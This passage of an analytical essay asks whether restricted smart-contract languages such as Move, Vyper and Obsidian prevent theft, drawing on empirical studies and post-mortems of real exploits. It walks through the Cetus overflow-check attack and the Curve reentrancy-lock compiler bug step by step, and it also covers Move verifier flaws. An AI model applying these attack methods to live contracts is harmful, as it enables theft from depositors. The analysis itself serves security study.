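| Casino: finished a program that compiled | 8 | 4 |
| Casino: lost tokens or created them from nothing | 4 of 8 | 4 of 4 |

If the languages made no difference, a gap in lost money as large as the one in the auction would appear in about two of every thousand experiments. Two of the successful Obsidian programmers first wrote code that lost money, then corrected it after getting an error message. Another Obsidian programmer refunded the old bid to the new bidder, and the program compiled because the money still went to someone.

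In the second task, a patient could take the same prescription to several pharmacies and collect the full number of refills from each. In Obsidian, changing one line fixes this by transferring ownership of the prescription from the patient to the pharmacy, and six of the Obsidian programmers found this fix. The Solidity programmers had to build a record shared by all the pharmacies, and only two succeeded.

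The casino task was harder and more open-ended, and Obsidian's advantage disappeared. Obsidian has an operator called `disown` that throws an asset away, which programmers occasionally need, though the tutorial warned against using it casually. All four people whose Obsidian programs compiled used it to discard tokens they should have kept or paid out. One added a comment that the code "just throws the bettor's money away and hopes they find it eventually". Removing `disown` would not have solved the problem, because a programmer could write a contract that accepts anything and never returns it. The Obsidian programmers also took longer, averaging 64 minutes compared with 37. Four programs are too few for a firm conclusion, but only the faster half of the Obsidian group had time for this task, so these four were probably not the weakest programmers.

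Some features of the experiment favoured Obsidian. Nobody could run or test their code, and testing might have exposed some of the Solidity bugs. The Solidity programmers also had to follow a pattern that guards against reentrancy, a precaution that Obsidian's blockchain does not need. But the Solidity group had more programming experience, with a median of 9.2 years against 5.0. Testing might also have helped less than one would expect, since people in an earlier study by Delmolino and colleagues, cited by Coblenz and colleagues, could run their contracts on a blockchain and still finished with code that lost assets.

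Resource types can stop beginners from losing money in a small contract. They work less well when the programmer is stuck and the language offers a way to suppress compiler errors.

### Five million lines of Rust

The largest comparison comes from outside blockchains and involves Rust, a general-purpose language. Rust's compiler restricts data by limiting which parts of a program may change or release a piece of memory. It does not restrict computation, and a Rust program can open any file that a C program can. Rust's rules target memory-safety flaws, in which a program reads or writes memory outside the area meant for it, as when the overlong delivery note overwrote the order total.

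Vander Stoep (2025) reports in *Rust in Android* that Google had found one potential memory-safety flaw in about 5 million lines of Rust in Android, its phone operating system. That is 0.2 per million lines, compared with Google's historical figure of about 1,000 per million for C and C++. He describes the difference as more than a thousandfold, and the printed figures differ by a factor of 5,000.

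An estimate based on one flaw is imprecise, but even the upper end of the plausible range is far below the C and C++ rate. By the usual statistical formula for rare events, one flaw in 5 million lines is compatible with a true rate as high as 1.1 per million, about 900 times lower than in C and C++. A more serious worry is that people have had decades to look for flaws in the C and C++ code and only a few years to look in the Rust code. If they have found only one in a hundred of the Rust flaws, the true rate would be 20 per million lines, a fiftieth of the C and C++ rate.

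The comparison also doesn't control for which components engineers choose to write in Rust, and they may choose ones that are easier to write safely. Vander Stoep's figures on everyday development are better matched because they cover changes of similar size by Google's own Android developers, many of whom use both languages. Developers had to withdraw medium and large Rust changes about a quarter as often as C++ ones. This suggests Rust also prevents some ordinary mistakes, although a withdrawn change may not involve a security flaw.

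The one Rust flaw was a buffer overflow in CrabbyAVIF, a library that reads images. Google caught it before release, and attackers could not have exploited it on a standard Android phone. Android's memory allocator puts an inaccessible page next to each large block, so the overflow would have crashed the program without corrupting other data.

About 4% of Android's Rust code is in blocks marked `unsafe`, where the programmer can use operations that the compiler can't check. This resembles Obsidian's `disown`, but Google's engineers seem to have handled `unsafe` much better than the casino programmers handled `disown`. Google's engineers had reviewers, training and far more time.

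The Android result supports the idea that restricting what a program can do with data removes nearly all of one class of bug. It is much weaker evidence about bugs other than memory-safety flaws, which made up more than 80% of Android vulnerabilities in 2025. It is also evidence about honest mistakes, whereas a hostile author who is allowed to write Rust can use `unsafe` or read any file the program has permission to read. The result matters more for the host, because writing its interpreter in Rust avoids many of the memory bugs that lead to a sandbox escape.

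### Missing checks as a virtue and as a defect

No comparable experiment exists for Move, but *Comparing Smart Contract Paradigms* (Vaccargiu, Pinna and colleagues, 2026) compares Move and Solidity versions of 12 contracts. They come from a public collection in which one team writes the same contract in several languages, so the programmers' skill and style should be similar. The researchers counted explicit security checks, such as `require(caller == owner)`.

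| Average per contract | Solidity | Move (on Sui) |
|---|---|---|
| Lines of code | 33.9 | 49.8 |
| Explicit security checks | 6.0 | 3.8 |
| Checks as a share of lines | 16.8% | 6.7% |

The share of lines used for checks fell by 60%, but the number of checks fell by only 38%. Much of the difference arises because Move code is longer, with extra lines to state types and move resources around. A Move contract of average length that kept all six checks would still use only about 12% of its lines for them.

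Vaccargiu and colleagues counted checks, not bugs. A Move contract may contain fewer checks because it needs fewer, as with the vault stored under its owner's address, or because its author forgot one. By this measure, the missing check at Typus Finance would have improved Move's score. The researchers leave vulnerability rates in deployed contracts to future work. They also surveyed 11 students who had written contracts in both languages, and 10 felt more confident in the safety of Move. This helps predict whether programmers will accept the language, but it isn't evidence that Move contracts have fewer bugs.

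Song, Chen and colleagues (2024), in *Empirical Study of Move Smart Contract Security*, worked with a security company to audit 652 Move contracts from 92 projects by hand. They identified eight types of defect, four of them previously unreported, and built a tool called MoveScan to search for all eight. It found 97,028 defects in 37,302 contracts already in use on Aptos and Sui, or about 2.6 per contract.

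The eight defect types in that total include security risks and functional faults, but also code that misleads users or merely wastes computation. Only some of these defects put money at risk, and the total doesn't show how many. HackenProof describes arithmetic defects as one of the study's two most common and financially dangerous categories. MoveScan's precision of 98.85% means that nearly everything it flags matches one of the eight patterns, whether or not an attacker could profit from it.

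A follow-up study focused on more dangerous flaws. According to G2MU and Matviiva's *Move Smart Contract Security Guide*, Zhang and colleagues (2025) added detectors for four types: leaking the capability to create coins, letting anyone create them, confusing one coin account with another, and misusing references to stored values. The detectors reported up to 20,778 matches in the same 37,302 contracts. Resource types don't prevent the unauthorised creation of coins, just as they would not have prevented Paxos's accident.

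In *MoveScanner*, Luo, Li and Li (2025) searched tens of thousands of Aptos contracts with another tool, which looks for five types of flaw.

| Flagged on Aptos by MoveScanner | Number | Share |
|---|---|---|
| Arithmetic overflow | 81,052 | 61.3% |
| One module changing another's records without a check on access | 24,460 | 18.5% |
| Leaked permissions | 13,118 | 10.0% |
| Ignored return values | 12,956 | 9.8% |
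| Lost resources | 466 | 0.4% |

Luo and colleagues warn that the overflow figure may be inflated. Their tool flags high-risk additions, subtractions and multiplications that have no explicit bounds check, but Move already aborts a transaction when one of these results doesn't fit, so the check would often be redundant. Without the overflow flags, 51,000 of the roughly 132,000 remain.

Vaccargiu and colleagues treat a missing check in a Move program as a sign of a safer language, while MoveScanner treats it as a vulnerability. The first interpretation is usually right for ordinary arithmetic, but it is wrong for permissions and for bit shifts, which Move doesn't check. Counting checks can't distinguish these cases under either interpretation.

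The small number of lost resources fits what resource types should do, but MoveScanner found only 4 of the 8 resource leaks planted in test contracts, so it may have missed others. The paper's text also reports 2,882 potential flaws in 20 open-source projects, while the accompanying table adds up to 224. The paper concludes that Move's type system eliminates 65% of traditional contract vulnerabilities, but none of its experiments measures this.

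Neither Move study included a Solidity sample, and a tool built for Move can't analyse Solidity directly. *Enhancing The Open Network* (2025) avoids this problem by running one tool, TONScanner, on contracts in two languages for the TON blockchain. FunC is the older, lower-level language, and Tact was designed to be easier to write. TONScanner flagged 8.4 defects per contract in 922 FunC contracts and 10.1 in 718 Tact contracts. Tact may have the higher count because it attracts less experienced programmers, because its contracts are longer, or because the tool recognises more of its patterns. The counts are per contract and weight every defect equally, so they give no reason to think that FunC contracts lose less money.

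### Half a million Solidity contracts

Comparing versions of a single language removes some of these difficulties. In *An Empirical Study of Impact of Solidity Compiler Updates on Vulnerabilities*, Kado, Yanai and colleagues (2023) used a tool called SmartCheck to look for three severe flaws in 503,572 Ethereum contracts with public Solidity source code, deployed up to August 2022. A contract with locked money can receive ether but has no function for sending it out. A contract that uses `tx.origin` for authentication can accept an impostor's commands. A contract with an unchecked call ignores the failure of a payment, so it may record a payment that never went through.

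| Solidity version | Contracts | Locked money | Uses `tx.origin` | Unchecked call |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0.4 | 210,426 | 10.7% | 0.6% | 1.7% |
| 0.5 | 83,390 | 33.6% | 1.8% | 32.9% |
| 0.6 | 54,402 | 6.7% | 3.0% | 39.1% |
| 0.7 | 22,442 | 5.7% | 4.9% | 38.1% |
| 0.8 | 132,912 | 6.9% | 1.9% | 22.0% |

The paper reports unchecked calls in 49.1% of version 0.6 contracts, but its own counts, 21,271 of 54,402, give 39.1%. Starting from 39.1%, the rate fell by 44% by version 0.8, less than the drop of more than half that the researchers describe.

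Kado and colleagues conclude that major compiler updates reduce vulnerabilities. The clearest case is locked money, which fell by four fifths between versions 0.5 and 0.6 and then stayed low, though they could not identify the reason. Whether unchecked calls declined depends on the starting version, because the rate in version 0.8 is far above the 1.7% in version 0.4. The researchers excluded version 0.4 because the rules for sending ether changed greatly after it, which is reasonable but leaves the largest group of contracts out of the trend. Uses of `tx.origin` are rare in all versions and follow no clear pattern.

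The three flaws don't include arithmetic overflow, which version 0.8 did stop by default. The study therefore provides little evidence about the change to Solidity that most resembles a new restriction.

SmartCheck also introduces errors. It flagged a function in OpenZeppelin's contract library for ignoring the result of a call, although the library checks that result in the next function. Every contract that copies the library triggers the same false alarm. Programmers also copy real flaws. Of 31 contracts in version 0.4 that SmartCheck flagged for unchecked calls during a few months of 2022, 23 were nearly identical. When Kado and colleagues removed copies from the contracts deployed between March and August 2022, the rate of unchecked calls fell in every version.

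Copying also makes it hard to separate the effects of language and age. Fewer than half of the version 0.5 contracts deployed in those six months were originals, compared with 91% for version 0.8. People who copy an old contract usually have to use its old compiler version too, so the figures for an old version partly reflect what people like to copy. The figures may also reflect who upgrades, since teams that upgrade promptly may be more careful in other ways and Kado and colleagues did not control for skill.

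A better language helps only if people use it. According to Kado and colleagues, Hwang and Ryu (2020) found that 98.14% of the contracts they studied, which went up to compiler version 0.5, lacked security patches for known vulnerabilities. A deployed contract's code can't change, so a compiler improvement reaches only contracts compiled afterwards. The online shop, by contrast, chooses the interpreter for its refund rules, so when it installs a repaired version, every old rule runs on it the next day.

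### Why a flagged defect is not an exploit

Tools can flag a contract that nobody can exploit. According to *V2E* (2026), a flaw is exploitable only if an attacker can trigger it under the conditions on the real blockchain, and a contract's developers usually also want to know whether triggering it is profitable.

In *Smart Contract Vulnerabilities: Vulnerable Does Not Imply Exploited* (2021), Perez and Livshits found that attackers had exploited only 1.98% of 23,327 contracts that six earlier research projects had reported as vulnerable. Losses were at most 8,487 ether, or 0.27% of the roughly 3 million ether at stake. Most of that 3 million was in a small number of contracts that nobody could exploit in practice.

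The 1.98% leaves out contracts that attackers could exploit but ignore because they hold no money. *Do Automated Fixes Truly Mitigate Smart Contract Exploits?* (2025) comes closer to measuring the exploitable proportion, because its researchers wrote the attacks themselves. They tried to exploit 143 contracts from a standard research collection, all labelled vulnerable, and succeeded with 91 (63.6%). In 30 of the others the flaw was only theoretical, for example because only the contract's owner could reach it or because reaching it did no harm. Another nine had no public function that let an attacker reach the flaw. Seven were labelled with the wrong compiler version, and the difference in Solidity's behaviour removed the reported flaw.

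These proportions describe different sets of contracts, so they don't conflict. Researchers picked the 143 to illustrate known flaws, while the 23,327 came from automated searches of the blockchain. Neither proportion shows what share of MoveScan's 97,028 defects would lead to theft, and there is no reason to expect that share to be the same for all languages. A tool that looks for suspicious patterns may flag a flaw even when the language stops attackers from exploiting it, as MoveScanner seems to have done with overflows. Counts of flags would then understate the benefit of the restriction.

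Tools also miss real flaws, because they search for known patterns and many thefts don't follow one. The lender that trusted a price from a small pool had no suspicious line in its code that a simple pattern-matcher could find. Human auditors do report such flaws. G2MU and Matviiva cite a database of 1,141 findings from more than 200 audits of Move contracts, and over 54% of them are business logic, input validation or calculation errors.

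That share doesn't show whether Move contracts have more logic errors than Solidity ones. If auditors find 60 logic errors in each of two languages, but also 40 cases of reentrancy in the first, logic errors make up 60% of findings in the first language and 100% in the second. Similarly, the share of Android flaws that involve memory safety can fall because those flaws have become rarer or because people have found more flaws of other kinds. Vander Stoep's rate per million lines avoids this problem.

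### Thefts divided by what?

It would be better to count thefts, since attackers are the ones who matter. But the ranking of two languages can then depend on what the number of thefts is divided by. The figures in this table are invented.

| Invented figures for one year | Language A | Language B |
|---|---|---|
| Contracts | 10,000 | 1,000 |
| Value held | $100 billion | $2 billion |
| Thefts | 50 | 4 |
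| Money stolen | $500 million | $40 million |
| Thefts per 1,000 contracts | 5 | 4 |
| Money stolen per $100 held | $0.50 | $2.00 |

Language B looks far safer by money stolen and slightly safer by thefts per contract, but it lost four times as much per dollar held. If $36 million of B's losses came from a single theft, delaying that theft until the following January would have reduced B's losses for the year to $0.20 per $100 held, and B would again have ranked safest.

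Dividing losses by value held suits a depositor, who wants to know the chance of losing each dollar. A developer choosing a language cares more about how often contracts like the planned one fail. Dividing by value held also partly corrects for thieves' preference for large targets, since a language whose contracts hold little money may have no thefts only because few thieves have looked. The correction is imperfect because contracts that hold more money also tend to get more audits, bug bounties and scrutiny from honest researchers, which reduce losses whatever the language.

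*Programming Languages Securing Ethereum's Value* (Lehmann, 2026) tracks the 1,000 Ethereum contracts that hold the most value. Most of them use Solidity 0.8, but those in version 0.6 hold a disproportionately large share of the value and include the contract that holds the deposits of people who help run Ethereum. Most of the value in Vyper contracts is in a few Curve pools and related contracts.

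Dividing thefts by these values would make Solidity 0.6, which lacks checked arithmetic by default, look safer than it is. Its large contracts have held money for years while exposed to attackers. Weaker contracts of the same age may have lost their money long ago and dropped out of the 1,000. The remaining contracts show that careful programmers can write a safe contract in an older language, but they are a poor guide to how safe the average one is. For Vyper, a single bug in a Curve pool could change the theft rate for the whole language.

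Theft data are a worse basis for comparing languages. G2MU and Matviiva list three major thefts from Move contracts in 2025, from Typus Finance, Cetus (about $223 million) and an exchange called Nemo (roughly $2.5 million). Cetus accounts for 97% of the sum. Estimates of losses across all languages vary. HackenProof cites the security company Hacken's figure of roughly $512 million lost to contract flaws in decentralised finance in 2025, while Zealynx put the year's losses at about $905 million. If both totals include the three Move thefts, Move's share was 45% by the first and 25% by the second. Either would be a very high share for a language whose blockchains hold a small part of the world's contract money, but without Cetus it would be about 1%.

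No sound exploit rate per language exists. Calculating one would require the language of every robbed contract, the value held in each language month by month, the age and audit history of the contracts, and a rule for counting bugs in compilers and shared libraries. Even with that data, Move's rate would be very uncertain. If its true average stayed constant, three thefts in one year would be compatible with anything from fewer than one a year to nearly nine.

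## When money was stolen from contracts in restricted languages, where was the bug?

Nobody can calculate a reliable theft rate for each language, but investigators can often trace a single theft to the faulty line within days, because a blockchain keeps every transaction and the code of most large contracts is public. The bug may be in the contract's own logic, the language implementation, a primitive that the contract calls, or the host's choice of what to expose. A language's rules directly affect only the contract's own logic, so the case for restriction is weaker if the big thefts came from bugs elsewhere.

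### Cetus: a check with the wrong limit

Cetus is the largest exchange on the Sui blockchain, and its contracts are written in Move. On 22 May 2025 an attacker drained about $223 million from it, the largest theft from decentralised finance that year, according to BlockSec's *#1 Cetus Incident* (2026). The bug was in one comparison inside a small arithmetic function, and the attacker didn't need to copy a coin or re-enter a function to exploit it.

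People who deposit tokens with Cetus choose a range of prices at which others may trade against their deposit. The exchange records the size of the deposit as a number called liquidity, then works out how many tokens the depositor owes for it. For a range above the current price, the formula is:

```
tokens owed = liquidity × (high − low) / (high × low)
```

Here `low` and `high` are the square roots of the prices at the two ends of the range. Contracts calculate in whole numbers, so Cetus stores these square roots multiplied by 2⁶⁴ to keep their fractional digits. To keep the scale correct, the code must also multiply the numerator by 2⁶⁴, which it does with a left shift.

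A left shift moves every binary digit towards the front of a number and fills the gap with zeros. Shifting by 64 places multiplies the number by 2⁶⁴, just as writing three zeros after a decimal number multiplies it by a thousand. But the number has only 256 binary digits, so any digit shifted past the front is lost.

Move aborts a transaction when an addition or multiplication gives too large a result, but not when a left shift loses digits, as Dedaub's *The Cetus AMM $200M Hack* (2025) explains. Dedaub calls this normal for languages with checked arithmetic. One reason is that programs that pack several small values into one number shift digits away on purpose. Cetus therefore wrote its own check for lost digits, a function called `checked_shlw`, in integer-mate, an open-source library that other Sui projects also used.

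The same error is easier to follow with 8-bit numbers, which run from 0 to 255, and a shift of two places, which multiplies by 4:

```
def checked_shift(n):
    if n > 192:              # should be: if n >= 64
        return "overflow"
    return (n * 4) % 256     # what an 8-bit shift leaves
```

Any number from 64 upward overflows, because 64 × 4 is 256.

| n | n × 4 | What the shift leaves | Faulty check (n > 192) | Correct check (n ≥ 64) |
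|---|---|---|---|---|
| 63 | 252 | 252 | passes | passes |
| 64 | 256 | 0 | passes | stops it |
| 65 | 260 | 4 | passes | stops it |
| 192 | 768 | 0 | passes | stops it |
| 193 | 772 | 4 | stops it | stops it |

The programmer probably chose 192 because in binary it is 11000000, with ones in exactly the two positions that the shift pushes out. Using it as a mask to test whether `n` has a one in either position would have been correct. Cetus instead compared the size of `n` with 192, but a number smaller than 192, such as 65, can still have a one in those positions.

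In the real function, the shift overflows for any number of 2¹⁹² or more, but the check rejected only numbers above 2²⁵⁶ − 2¹⁹². It therefore caught about one in 18 billion billion of the numbers it should have caught.

### How a huge deposit came to cost one unit

Suppose, still with 8-bit numbers, that liquidity times the price gap is 65 and the denominator is 10. The correct charge is 260 / 10, or 26 tokens. After the faulty shift, the code computes 4 / 10 and rounds up, so the depositor owes 1 token. The exchange still records the full liquidity and pays out 26 tokens when the depositor withdraws.

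Dedaub gives the numbers from one of the real transactions. The attacker asked for liquidity of about 10³⁴, chosen to make the product slightly larger than 2¹⁹². The correct charge was about 3 × 10²⁵ units of the token, more than anyone could have paid, but the code charged one unit, the smallest amount the token can represent. The attacker found the right liquidity using one of the contract's own functions.

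The rest of the attack prepared the ground and collected the money:

1. The attacker took 5.77 million SUI, the blockchain's own currency, from a pool, and promised to hand over 10.02 million haSUI (a related token worth roughly the same) before the transaction ended.
2. That enormous trade pushed the price of haSUI in the pool from about 1.06 SUI to almost nothing. The attacker could then choose a price range far above the current price, which a depositor funds with haSUI alone.
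3. The attacker deposited one unit of haSUI in that range and received the enormous liquidity.
4. The attacker withdrew the liquidity in portions that matched what the pool actually held, so the same formula now worked correctly and paid out real tokens.
5. The attacker delivered the haSUI promised at the start and, by ChainCatcher's account, kept about 10.02 million haSUI and 5.77 million SUI.

The attacker then repeated this in other pools. The Block's *Sui DEX Cetus says overlooked flaw in open-source library* reports that Cetus disabled its main pools within 30 minutes. The attacker had already moved about $60 million to Ethereum, according to MoveJay's *Inside The $223M Cetus Exploit* (2025). Sui's validators, who run the computers that process its transactions, froze the remaining $162 million or so by blocking the attacker's addresses, and later voted to return it.

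### Why nobody caught it, and why the first patch fell short

Dedaub reports that the audit firm OtterSec found almost the same bug two years earlier, in early 2023, in a version of the code written for Aptos. OtterSec warned that a shift could drop digits and recommended a checked version, which the team adopted. A couple of months later, the team moved the code to Sui and introduced the wrong limit into the checked version. OtterSec and another firm, MoveBit, then audited the Sui code without finding the flaw, and a Zellic audit in April 2025 reported nothing serious. Dedaub suspects that the library may have been outside the audits' scope. The function's name, `checked_shlw`, is also likely to make readers assume that the shift has been checked.

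The first repair was also wrong, but for only one input. According to *Dissecting the Cetus Protocol Exploit on Sui*, Cetus corrected the limit to 2¹⁹² but still rejected only inputs greater than the limit, so 2¹⁹² itself got through. In the 8-bit version, the test `n > 64` lets 64 through, and the result, 256, becomes 0. A second patch changed the test to "greater than or equal to". The remaining bug was probably hard to exploit, because liquidity times the price gap would have had to equal 2¹⁹² exactly, which can happen only when both are powers of two.

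Hacken's *[SUI] Full Math Library* describes another unchecked shift in the library. The function `mul_shl` multiplies two numbers, shifts the product left, and then checks that the result fits, but the shift may already have lost the digits that would have made the check fail. The maintainers marked the function as deprecated in September 2025. Hacken found no open-source project that called it, though several had copied the library that contains it. MoveJay names three other exchanges, Kriya, Momentum and Bluefin, that reportedly had related exposure to the `checked_shlw` flaw. OpenZeppelin has since published a shared arithmetic library for Sui and cites the Cetus theft as a reason for it.

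Move's designers made multiplication abort on overflow but let a left shift drop digits. If the code had multiplied by 2⁶⁴ instead of using the equivalent shift, Move would have aborted. MoveJay therefore goes too far in concluding that security is a property of engineering discipline and not of a language. A stricter Move could also abort ordinary shifts that lose digits, and offer a separate operator for programmers who want to lose them.

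The bug was therefore in a primitive, since the exchange called a library function that did not do what its name promised.

### Curve: correct source code, unprotected program

In the Cetus case a careful reader could have found the mistake in the source code, but the source code of the Curve contracts robbed on 30 July 2023 had no such mistake. Those contracts are written in Vyper, and their sensitive functions were marked `@nonreentrant('lock')` to request Vyper's reentrancy lock. Functions that name the same lock are supposed to share it, but the compiler failed to make them do so in Vyper versions 0.2.15, 0.2.16 and 0.3.0.

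In simplified form, the faulty compiler chose each lock's storage slot like this:

```
for function in contract:
    if function.lock_name is not None:
        function.lock_slot = next_slot    # missing: reuse the slot this name already has
        next_slot = next_slot + 1
```

Each function had its own lock. In *Vyper hack timeline*, Chen describes taking apart the compiled code of the first pool to lose money. The deposit function kept its lock in slot 0 and the withdrawal function kept its lock in slot 2. An attacker could not enter the withdrawal function twice, but could enter the deposit function during a withdrawal, because the deposit function checked a lock that the withdrawal had not set.

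BlockSec's *Curve Incident* (2024) reproduces the withdrawal function, which paid out ether before reducing the recorded total of shares. Suppose a simplified pool holds 100 ether from honest depositors, who own 100 shares, and Mallory, the thief from the earlier examples, has borrowed 200 ether.

| Step | Ether in the pool | Total shares on record | Mallory's shares |
|---|---|---|---|
| Before the attack | 100 | 100 | 0 |
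| Mallory deposits 100 ether | 200 | 200 | 100 |
| She withdraws, and the pool pays her 100 ether before cancelling her shares | 100 | 200 | 100 |
| During that payment she deposits 100 ether, and the pool gives her two shares per ether | 200 | 400 | 300 |
| The withdrawal finishes and sets the total to the figure it read at the start, minus 100 | 200 | 100 | 200 |
| She cashes in 100 shares, which now look like the whole pool | 0 | 0 | 100 |

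Mallory has put in 200 ether and taken out 300, and the honest depositors have lost everything. If the lock had worked, the deposit she made during the payment would have reverted.

The real attack on the pool that traded ether against the token pETH followed the same pattern. The attacker deposited 40,000 ether and got 32,431 shares, then deposited another 40,000 ether while withdrawing the first deposit and got 82,182 shares. Redeeming only 10,273 of those returned 47,507 ether and 1,185 pETH. The attacker made about $11 million.

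Attackers could profit only where the lock was the sole protection. If the pool had updated all its records before paying out, the split lock would have done no harm. The developers had reasonably relied on a feature that the language advertised, but they had no other protection when it failed. BlockSec calls this the first time a compiler bug caused a significant financial loss on a blockchain.

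### Why a fix from 2021 did not help in 2023

According to Vyper's post-mortem, the developers introduced the flaw while fixing another bug. They were rebuilding the compiler in stages, and for a while two parts of it calculated storage positions separately. In version 0.2.14 the two calculations gave different results, so a lock could be assigned the same slot as an ordinary variable. A user noticed when tests failed on the code of Yearn, an investment protocol, whose withdrawal lock shared a slot with its management fee. The developers withdrew that version and merged the two calculations in 0.2.15, but in the process they deleted the lines that gave each lock name a single slot.

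Nobody noticed the fault for four months. Named locks exist only so that several functions can share one, but the compiler's tests never checked that a call to one function would block calls to the others sharing its lock. Version 0.3.1 corrected the fault and added the missing test in November 2021. But the developers described part of the change as removing unused storage slots and didn't realise what the fault meant for contracts already in use.

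The corrected compiler did not fix contracts already deployed. Their owners would have had to move the money to new contracts, and nobody told them to. Unlock Blockchain reported that the security firm Ancilia counted 460 contracts built with the three versions. The formal advisory, OSV's *Vyper has incorrectly allocated named re-entrancy locks* (2023), appeared on 9 August, ten days after the thefts and 20 months after the fix.

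Estimates of the loss differ mainly in whether they count money that was returned. Halborn puts it at about $70 million at first and $52 million after some of those who drained the pools returned the money, and Quiroz-Gutierrez (2023), in *Fortune*, also gives $52 million. Curve's administrators could not pause the pools, so the rescuers could only drain them first and return the money. Chen's group identified the faulty versions about two hours after the first suspicions, and named them publicly when rumours were already spreading. Others emptied a large remaining pool three hours later, shortly before the rescuers were ready. Chen thinks another half hour would have saved $18 million.

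Chen disagrees with those who said that only formal verification could have prevented the bug, and points out that a simple test would have caught it. The post-mortem supports this, but also proposes verifying the compiler's output. Either method would have to cover old compiler versions, because contracts built with them may still hold money.

The bug was in the language implementation. It was an honest mistake that harmed many honest contract authors at once. A Solidity programmer who forgets a lock exposes one contract, but when Vyper's compiler mishandled locks, every contract that relied on a shared lock lost part of its protection.

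### Code that Move's verifier did not see

Compiler bugs like Vyper's matter to authors who want protection. A hostile author can skip the compiler, because a blockchain accepts compiled instructions, called bytecode, that anyone can write by hand. In Move, every validator therefore runs a verifier that checks the bytecode again before publishing it. Move's guarantees about coins depend on this verifier.

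Zellic's *The Billion Dollar Bug* lists about a dozen checks that the verifier performs, and says that explaining them all could fill a small book. Before some of the most important checks, the verifier works out which instructions can follow which. It then follows every possible path through the code to confirm, for example, that none discards a value the program isn't allowed to discard.

Zellic found in March 2023 that the map could lack a path. The helper function that lists what can follow an instruction stopped early near the end of functions of almost the maximum length, about 65,000 instructions, and listed nothing after the last instruction. If that instruction was a jump, the verifier never checked what happened after the jump, but the virtual machine still ran the code that followed. The developers had added the early stop to keep a counter from overflowing, so this bug, like the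 one at Cetus, was in a safeguard against overflow. The fix was to list the jump's destination as usual.

The flaw could have let an attacker keep a flash loan, which can be any size, needs no collateral and must be repaid within the same transaction. Many Move lenders enforce repayment with a receipt, a value that the borrower can neither store nor discard, so the only way to finish the transaction is to return it with the money. An attacker who got past the verifier could have thrown the receipt away. Zellic also showed how a thief could pay with a coin, keep a reference to it, and use that reference to take the money back.

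The flaw dated from October 2022 and affected all the Move blockchains, including Aptos, which was already running. Sui's developers fixed it five days after the report, before Sui opened to the public. Move's virtual machine has optional extra checks that run while the program does, and these stopped the simplest attacks but not the one that takes back a payment.

Researchers found other flaws in the same machinery:

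- *Reference checks.* The part of the verifier that tracks references numbered a function's variables with an 8-bit counter, according to Coinlive's *The Story of a High Vulnerability in Move Reference Safety*. A function with more than 256 parameters and local variables made the counter wrap round and start again.
- *Crashes.* The Hacker News' *Critical Flaw Reported in Move Virtual Machine Powering the Aptos Blockchain Network* (2022) describes a flaw that could crash the computers running Aptos. Numen Cyber Labs published it in the month that Aptos launched, after the developers had patched it.
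- *An endless loop.* CertiK, another audit firm, found in 2023 that about 100 bytes of input could send Sui's verifier into an infinite loop and stop the whole network, even after a restart. Sui fixed this within a day and paid a reward of $500,000, as CryptoSlate's *Sui awards $500k to CertiK for uncovering critical ‘HamsterWheel’ vulnerability* reports.
- *A recent case.* In July 2026 Antipov (2026), in *Взломать блокчейн на $70 миллиардов?*, a Russian news report, described how ethical hackers had found an error in Aptos Move that could have hit stablecoins, lending and the bridges that carry assets between blockchains.

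These flaws are better evidence about hostile authors than the Curve or Cetus thefts are, because a stranger could have exploited each one by submitting crafted input. They also show a drawback of restriction. Enforcing Move's stricter rules takes more code, and any of that code can be wrong. Ethereum's virtual machine does not guarantee that a program cannot copy a coin, so it needs no verifier to enforce that rule. Zellic audited the exchange Liquidswap and found its flash loans correct, but noted in *Flashloan implementation depends on Aptos VM correctness* that they depend heavily on the virtual machine and the verifier.

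### Counterfeit coins

Thieves have also found such flaws first. Flow is a blockchain whose language, Cadence, has resource types like Move's. On 27 December 2025 an attacker created $3.9 million in counterfeit tokens on Flow, according to Clawditor (2026). The attacker exploited a type confusion bug in Cadence's runtime, version 1.8.8 and earlier, that could make the runtime treat a value of one type as another. A language can forbid programs to copy coins, but the ban doesn't apply to a coin that the runtime treats as ordinary data.

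Something similar happened in October 2026 on Initia, which runs Move. EconoTimes' *Initia Ties $2.7 Million Exploit to MoveVM Script-Cache Flaw* reports Initia's explanation that a fault in how the virtual machine cached scripts let an attacker bypass its checks. The attacker created balances with no assets behind them, moved about $2.7 million to Ethereum and exchanged it for 1,135 ether. Initia halted its network.

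The affected tokens on Initia included wrapped ether and two dollar tokens, which probably had little in common except the virtual machine. On Ethereum, each token usually has its own contract, so a thief who can forge one token cannot necessarily forge another. When the rule is built into the language, token authors do not have to enforce it themselves, but one fault can break it for every token.

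### Errors that compile cleanly

Even a perfect verifier accepts contracts whose logic is wrong. OpenZeppelin collected four patterns of such errors from audits of Sui contracts. Code with these errors compiles and passes basic tests. OpenZeppelin doesn't report that anyone stole money through them.

Lombard Finance limited how many tokens a minter could create in each period, say to 1,000. The contract stored the `limit` and the amount `left`, and it was supposed to reset `left` to 1,000 at the start of each new period. The author wrote `left = limit`. In Solidity that line would copy a number, but in this Move function both names were references to stored fields, so the line made `left` refer to the limit itself. When the minter next created 1,000 tokens, the contract subtracted them from the limit, which fell to zero, and nobody could mint again. The correct line is `*left = *limit`, where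 the asterisks refer to the stored values. A Solidity programmer who learns Move can easily make this mistake, so here the safer language introduced a new bug.

At Navi, a lender, the withdrawal function took a pool and a number that identified the asset. Move guaranteed that a bitcoin pool held only bitcoin, but the function never checked that the number matched the pool. A customer could therefore pass in the bitcoin pool with the number for a digital dollar, and the contract would deduct one dollar from the customer's account and pay out one bitcoin. The fix is to work out the asset from the pool's type instead of asking the caller. An auditor of Kuna Labs found a related error that let somebody settle a borrower's loan against the wrong pool, repay nothing, and still collect the borrower's collateral.

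In the third pattern, the bug is one wrong keyword. In Move on Sui, any module can call a `public` function, but only modules in the same package can call a `public(package)` function. SuiFrens, a game with digital creatures, made players wait before mixing the same creature again. The helper function that recorded the last mixing was `public`, so any player could call it directly and reset the waiting period.

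The last pattern concerns receipts for flash loans. Cetus also let people leave orders to sell one token for another, and it lent out the tokens waiting in those orders. The borrower had to hand back a receipt with the repayment, but the function never checked that the receipt was for the order being repaid. Suppose Alice has an order to sell 1,000 USDC (a digital dollar) for SUI. Mallory borrows the USDC, repays in SUI to an order of her own, and withdraws the SUI. She keeps the 1,000 USDC, and Alice has nothing. One added line that compares the two order numbers prevents this.

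Move's rules worked as designed in all of these cases. The receipt rule forced Mallory to call the repayment function, but that function paid the wrong person. Programmers may also assume such a rule guarantees more than it does, and stop checking too early.

### The cases by place

| Case | Outcome | Place of the bug | Repair |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cetus pools, 2025 | $223 million stolen | primitive: a shared arithmetic library | reject every number from 2¹⁹² upward |
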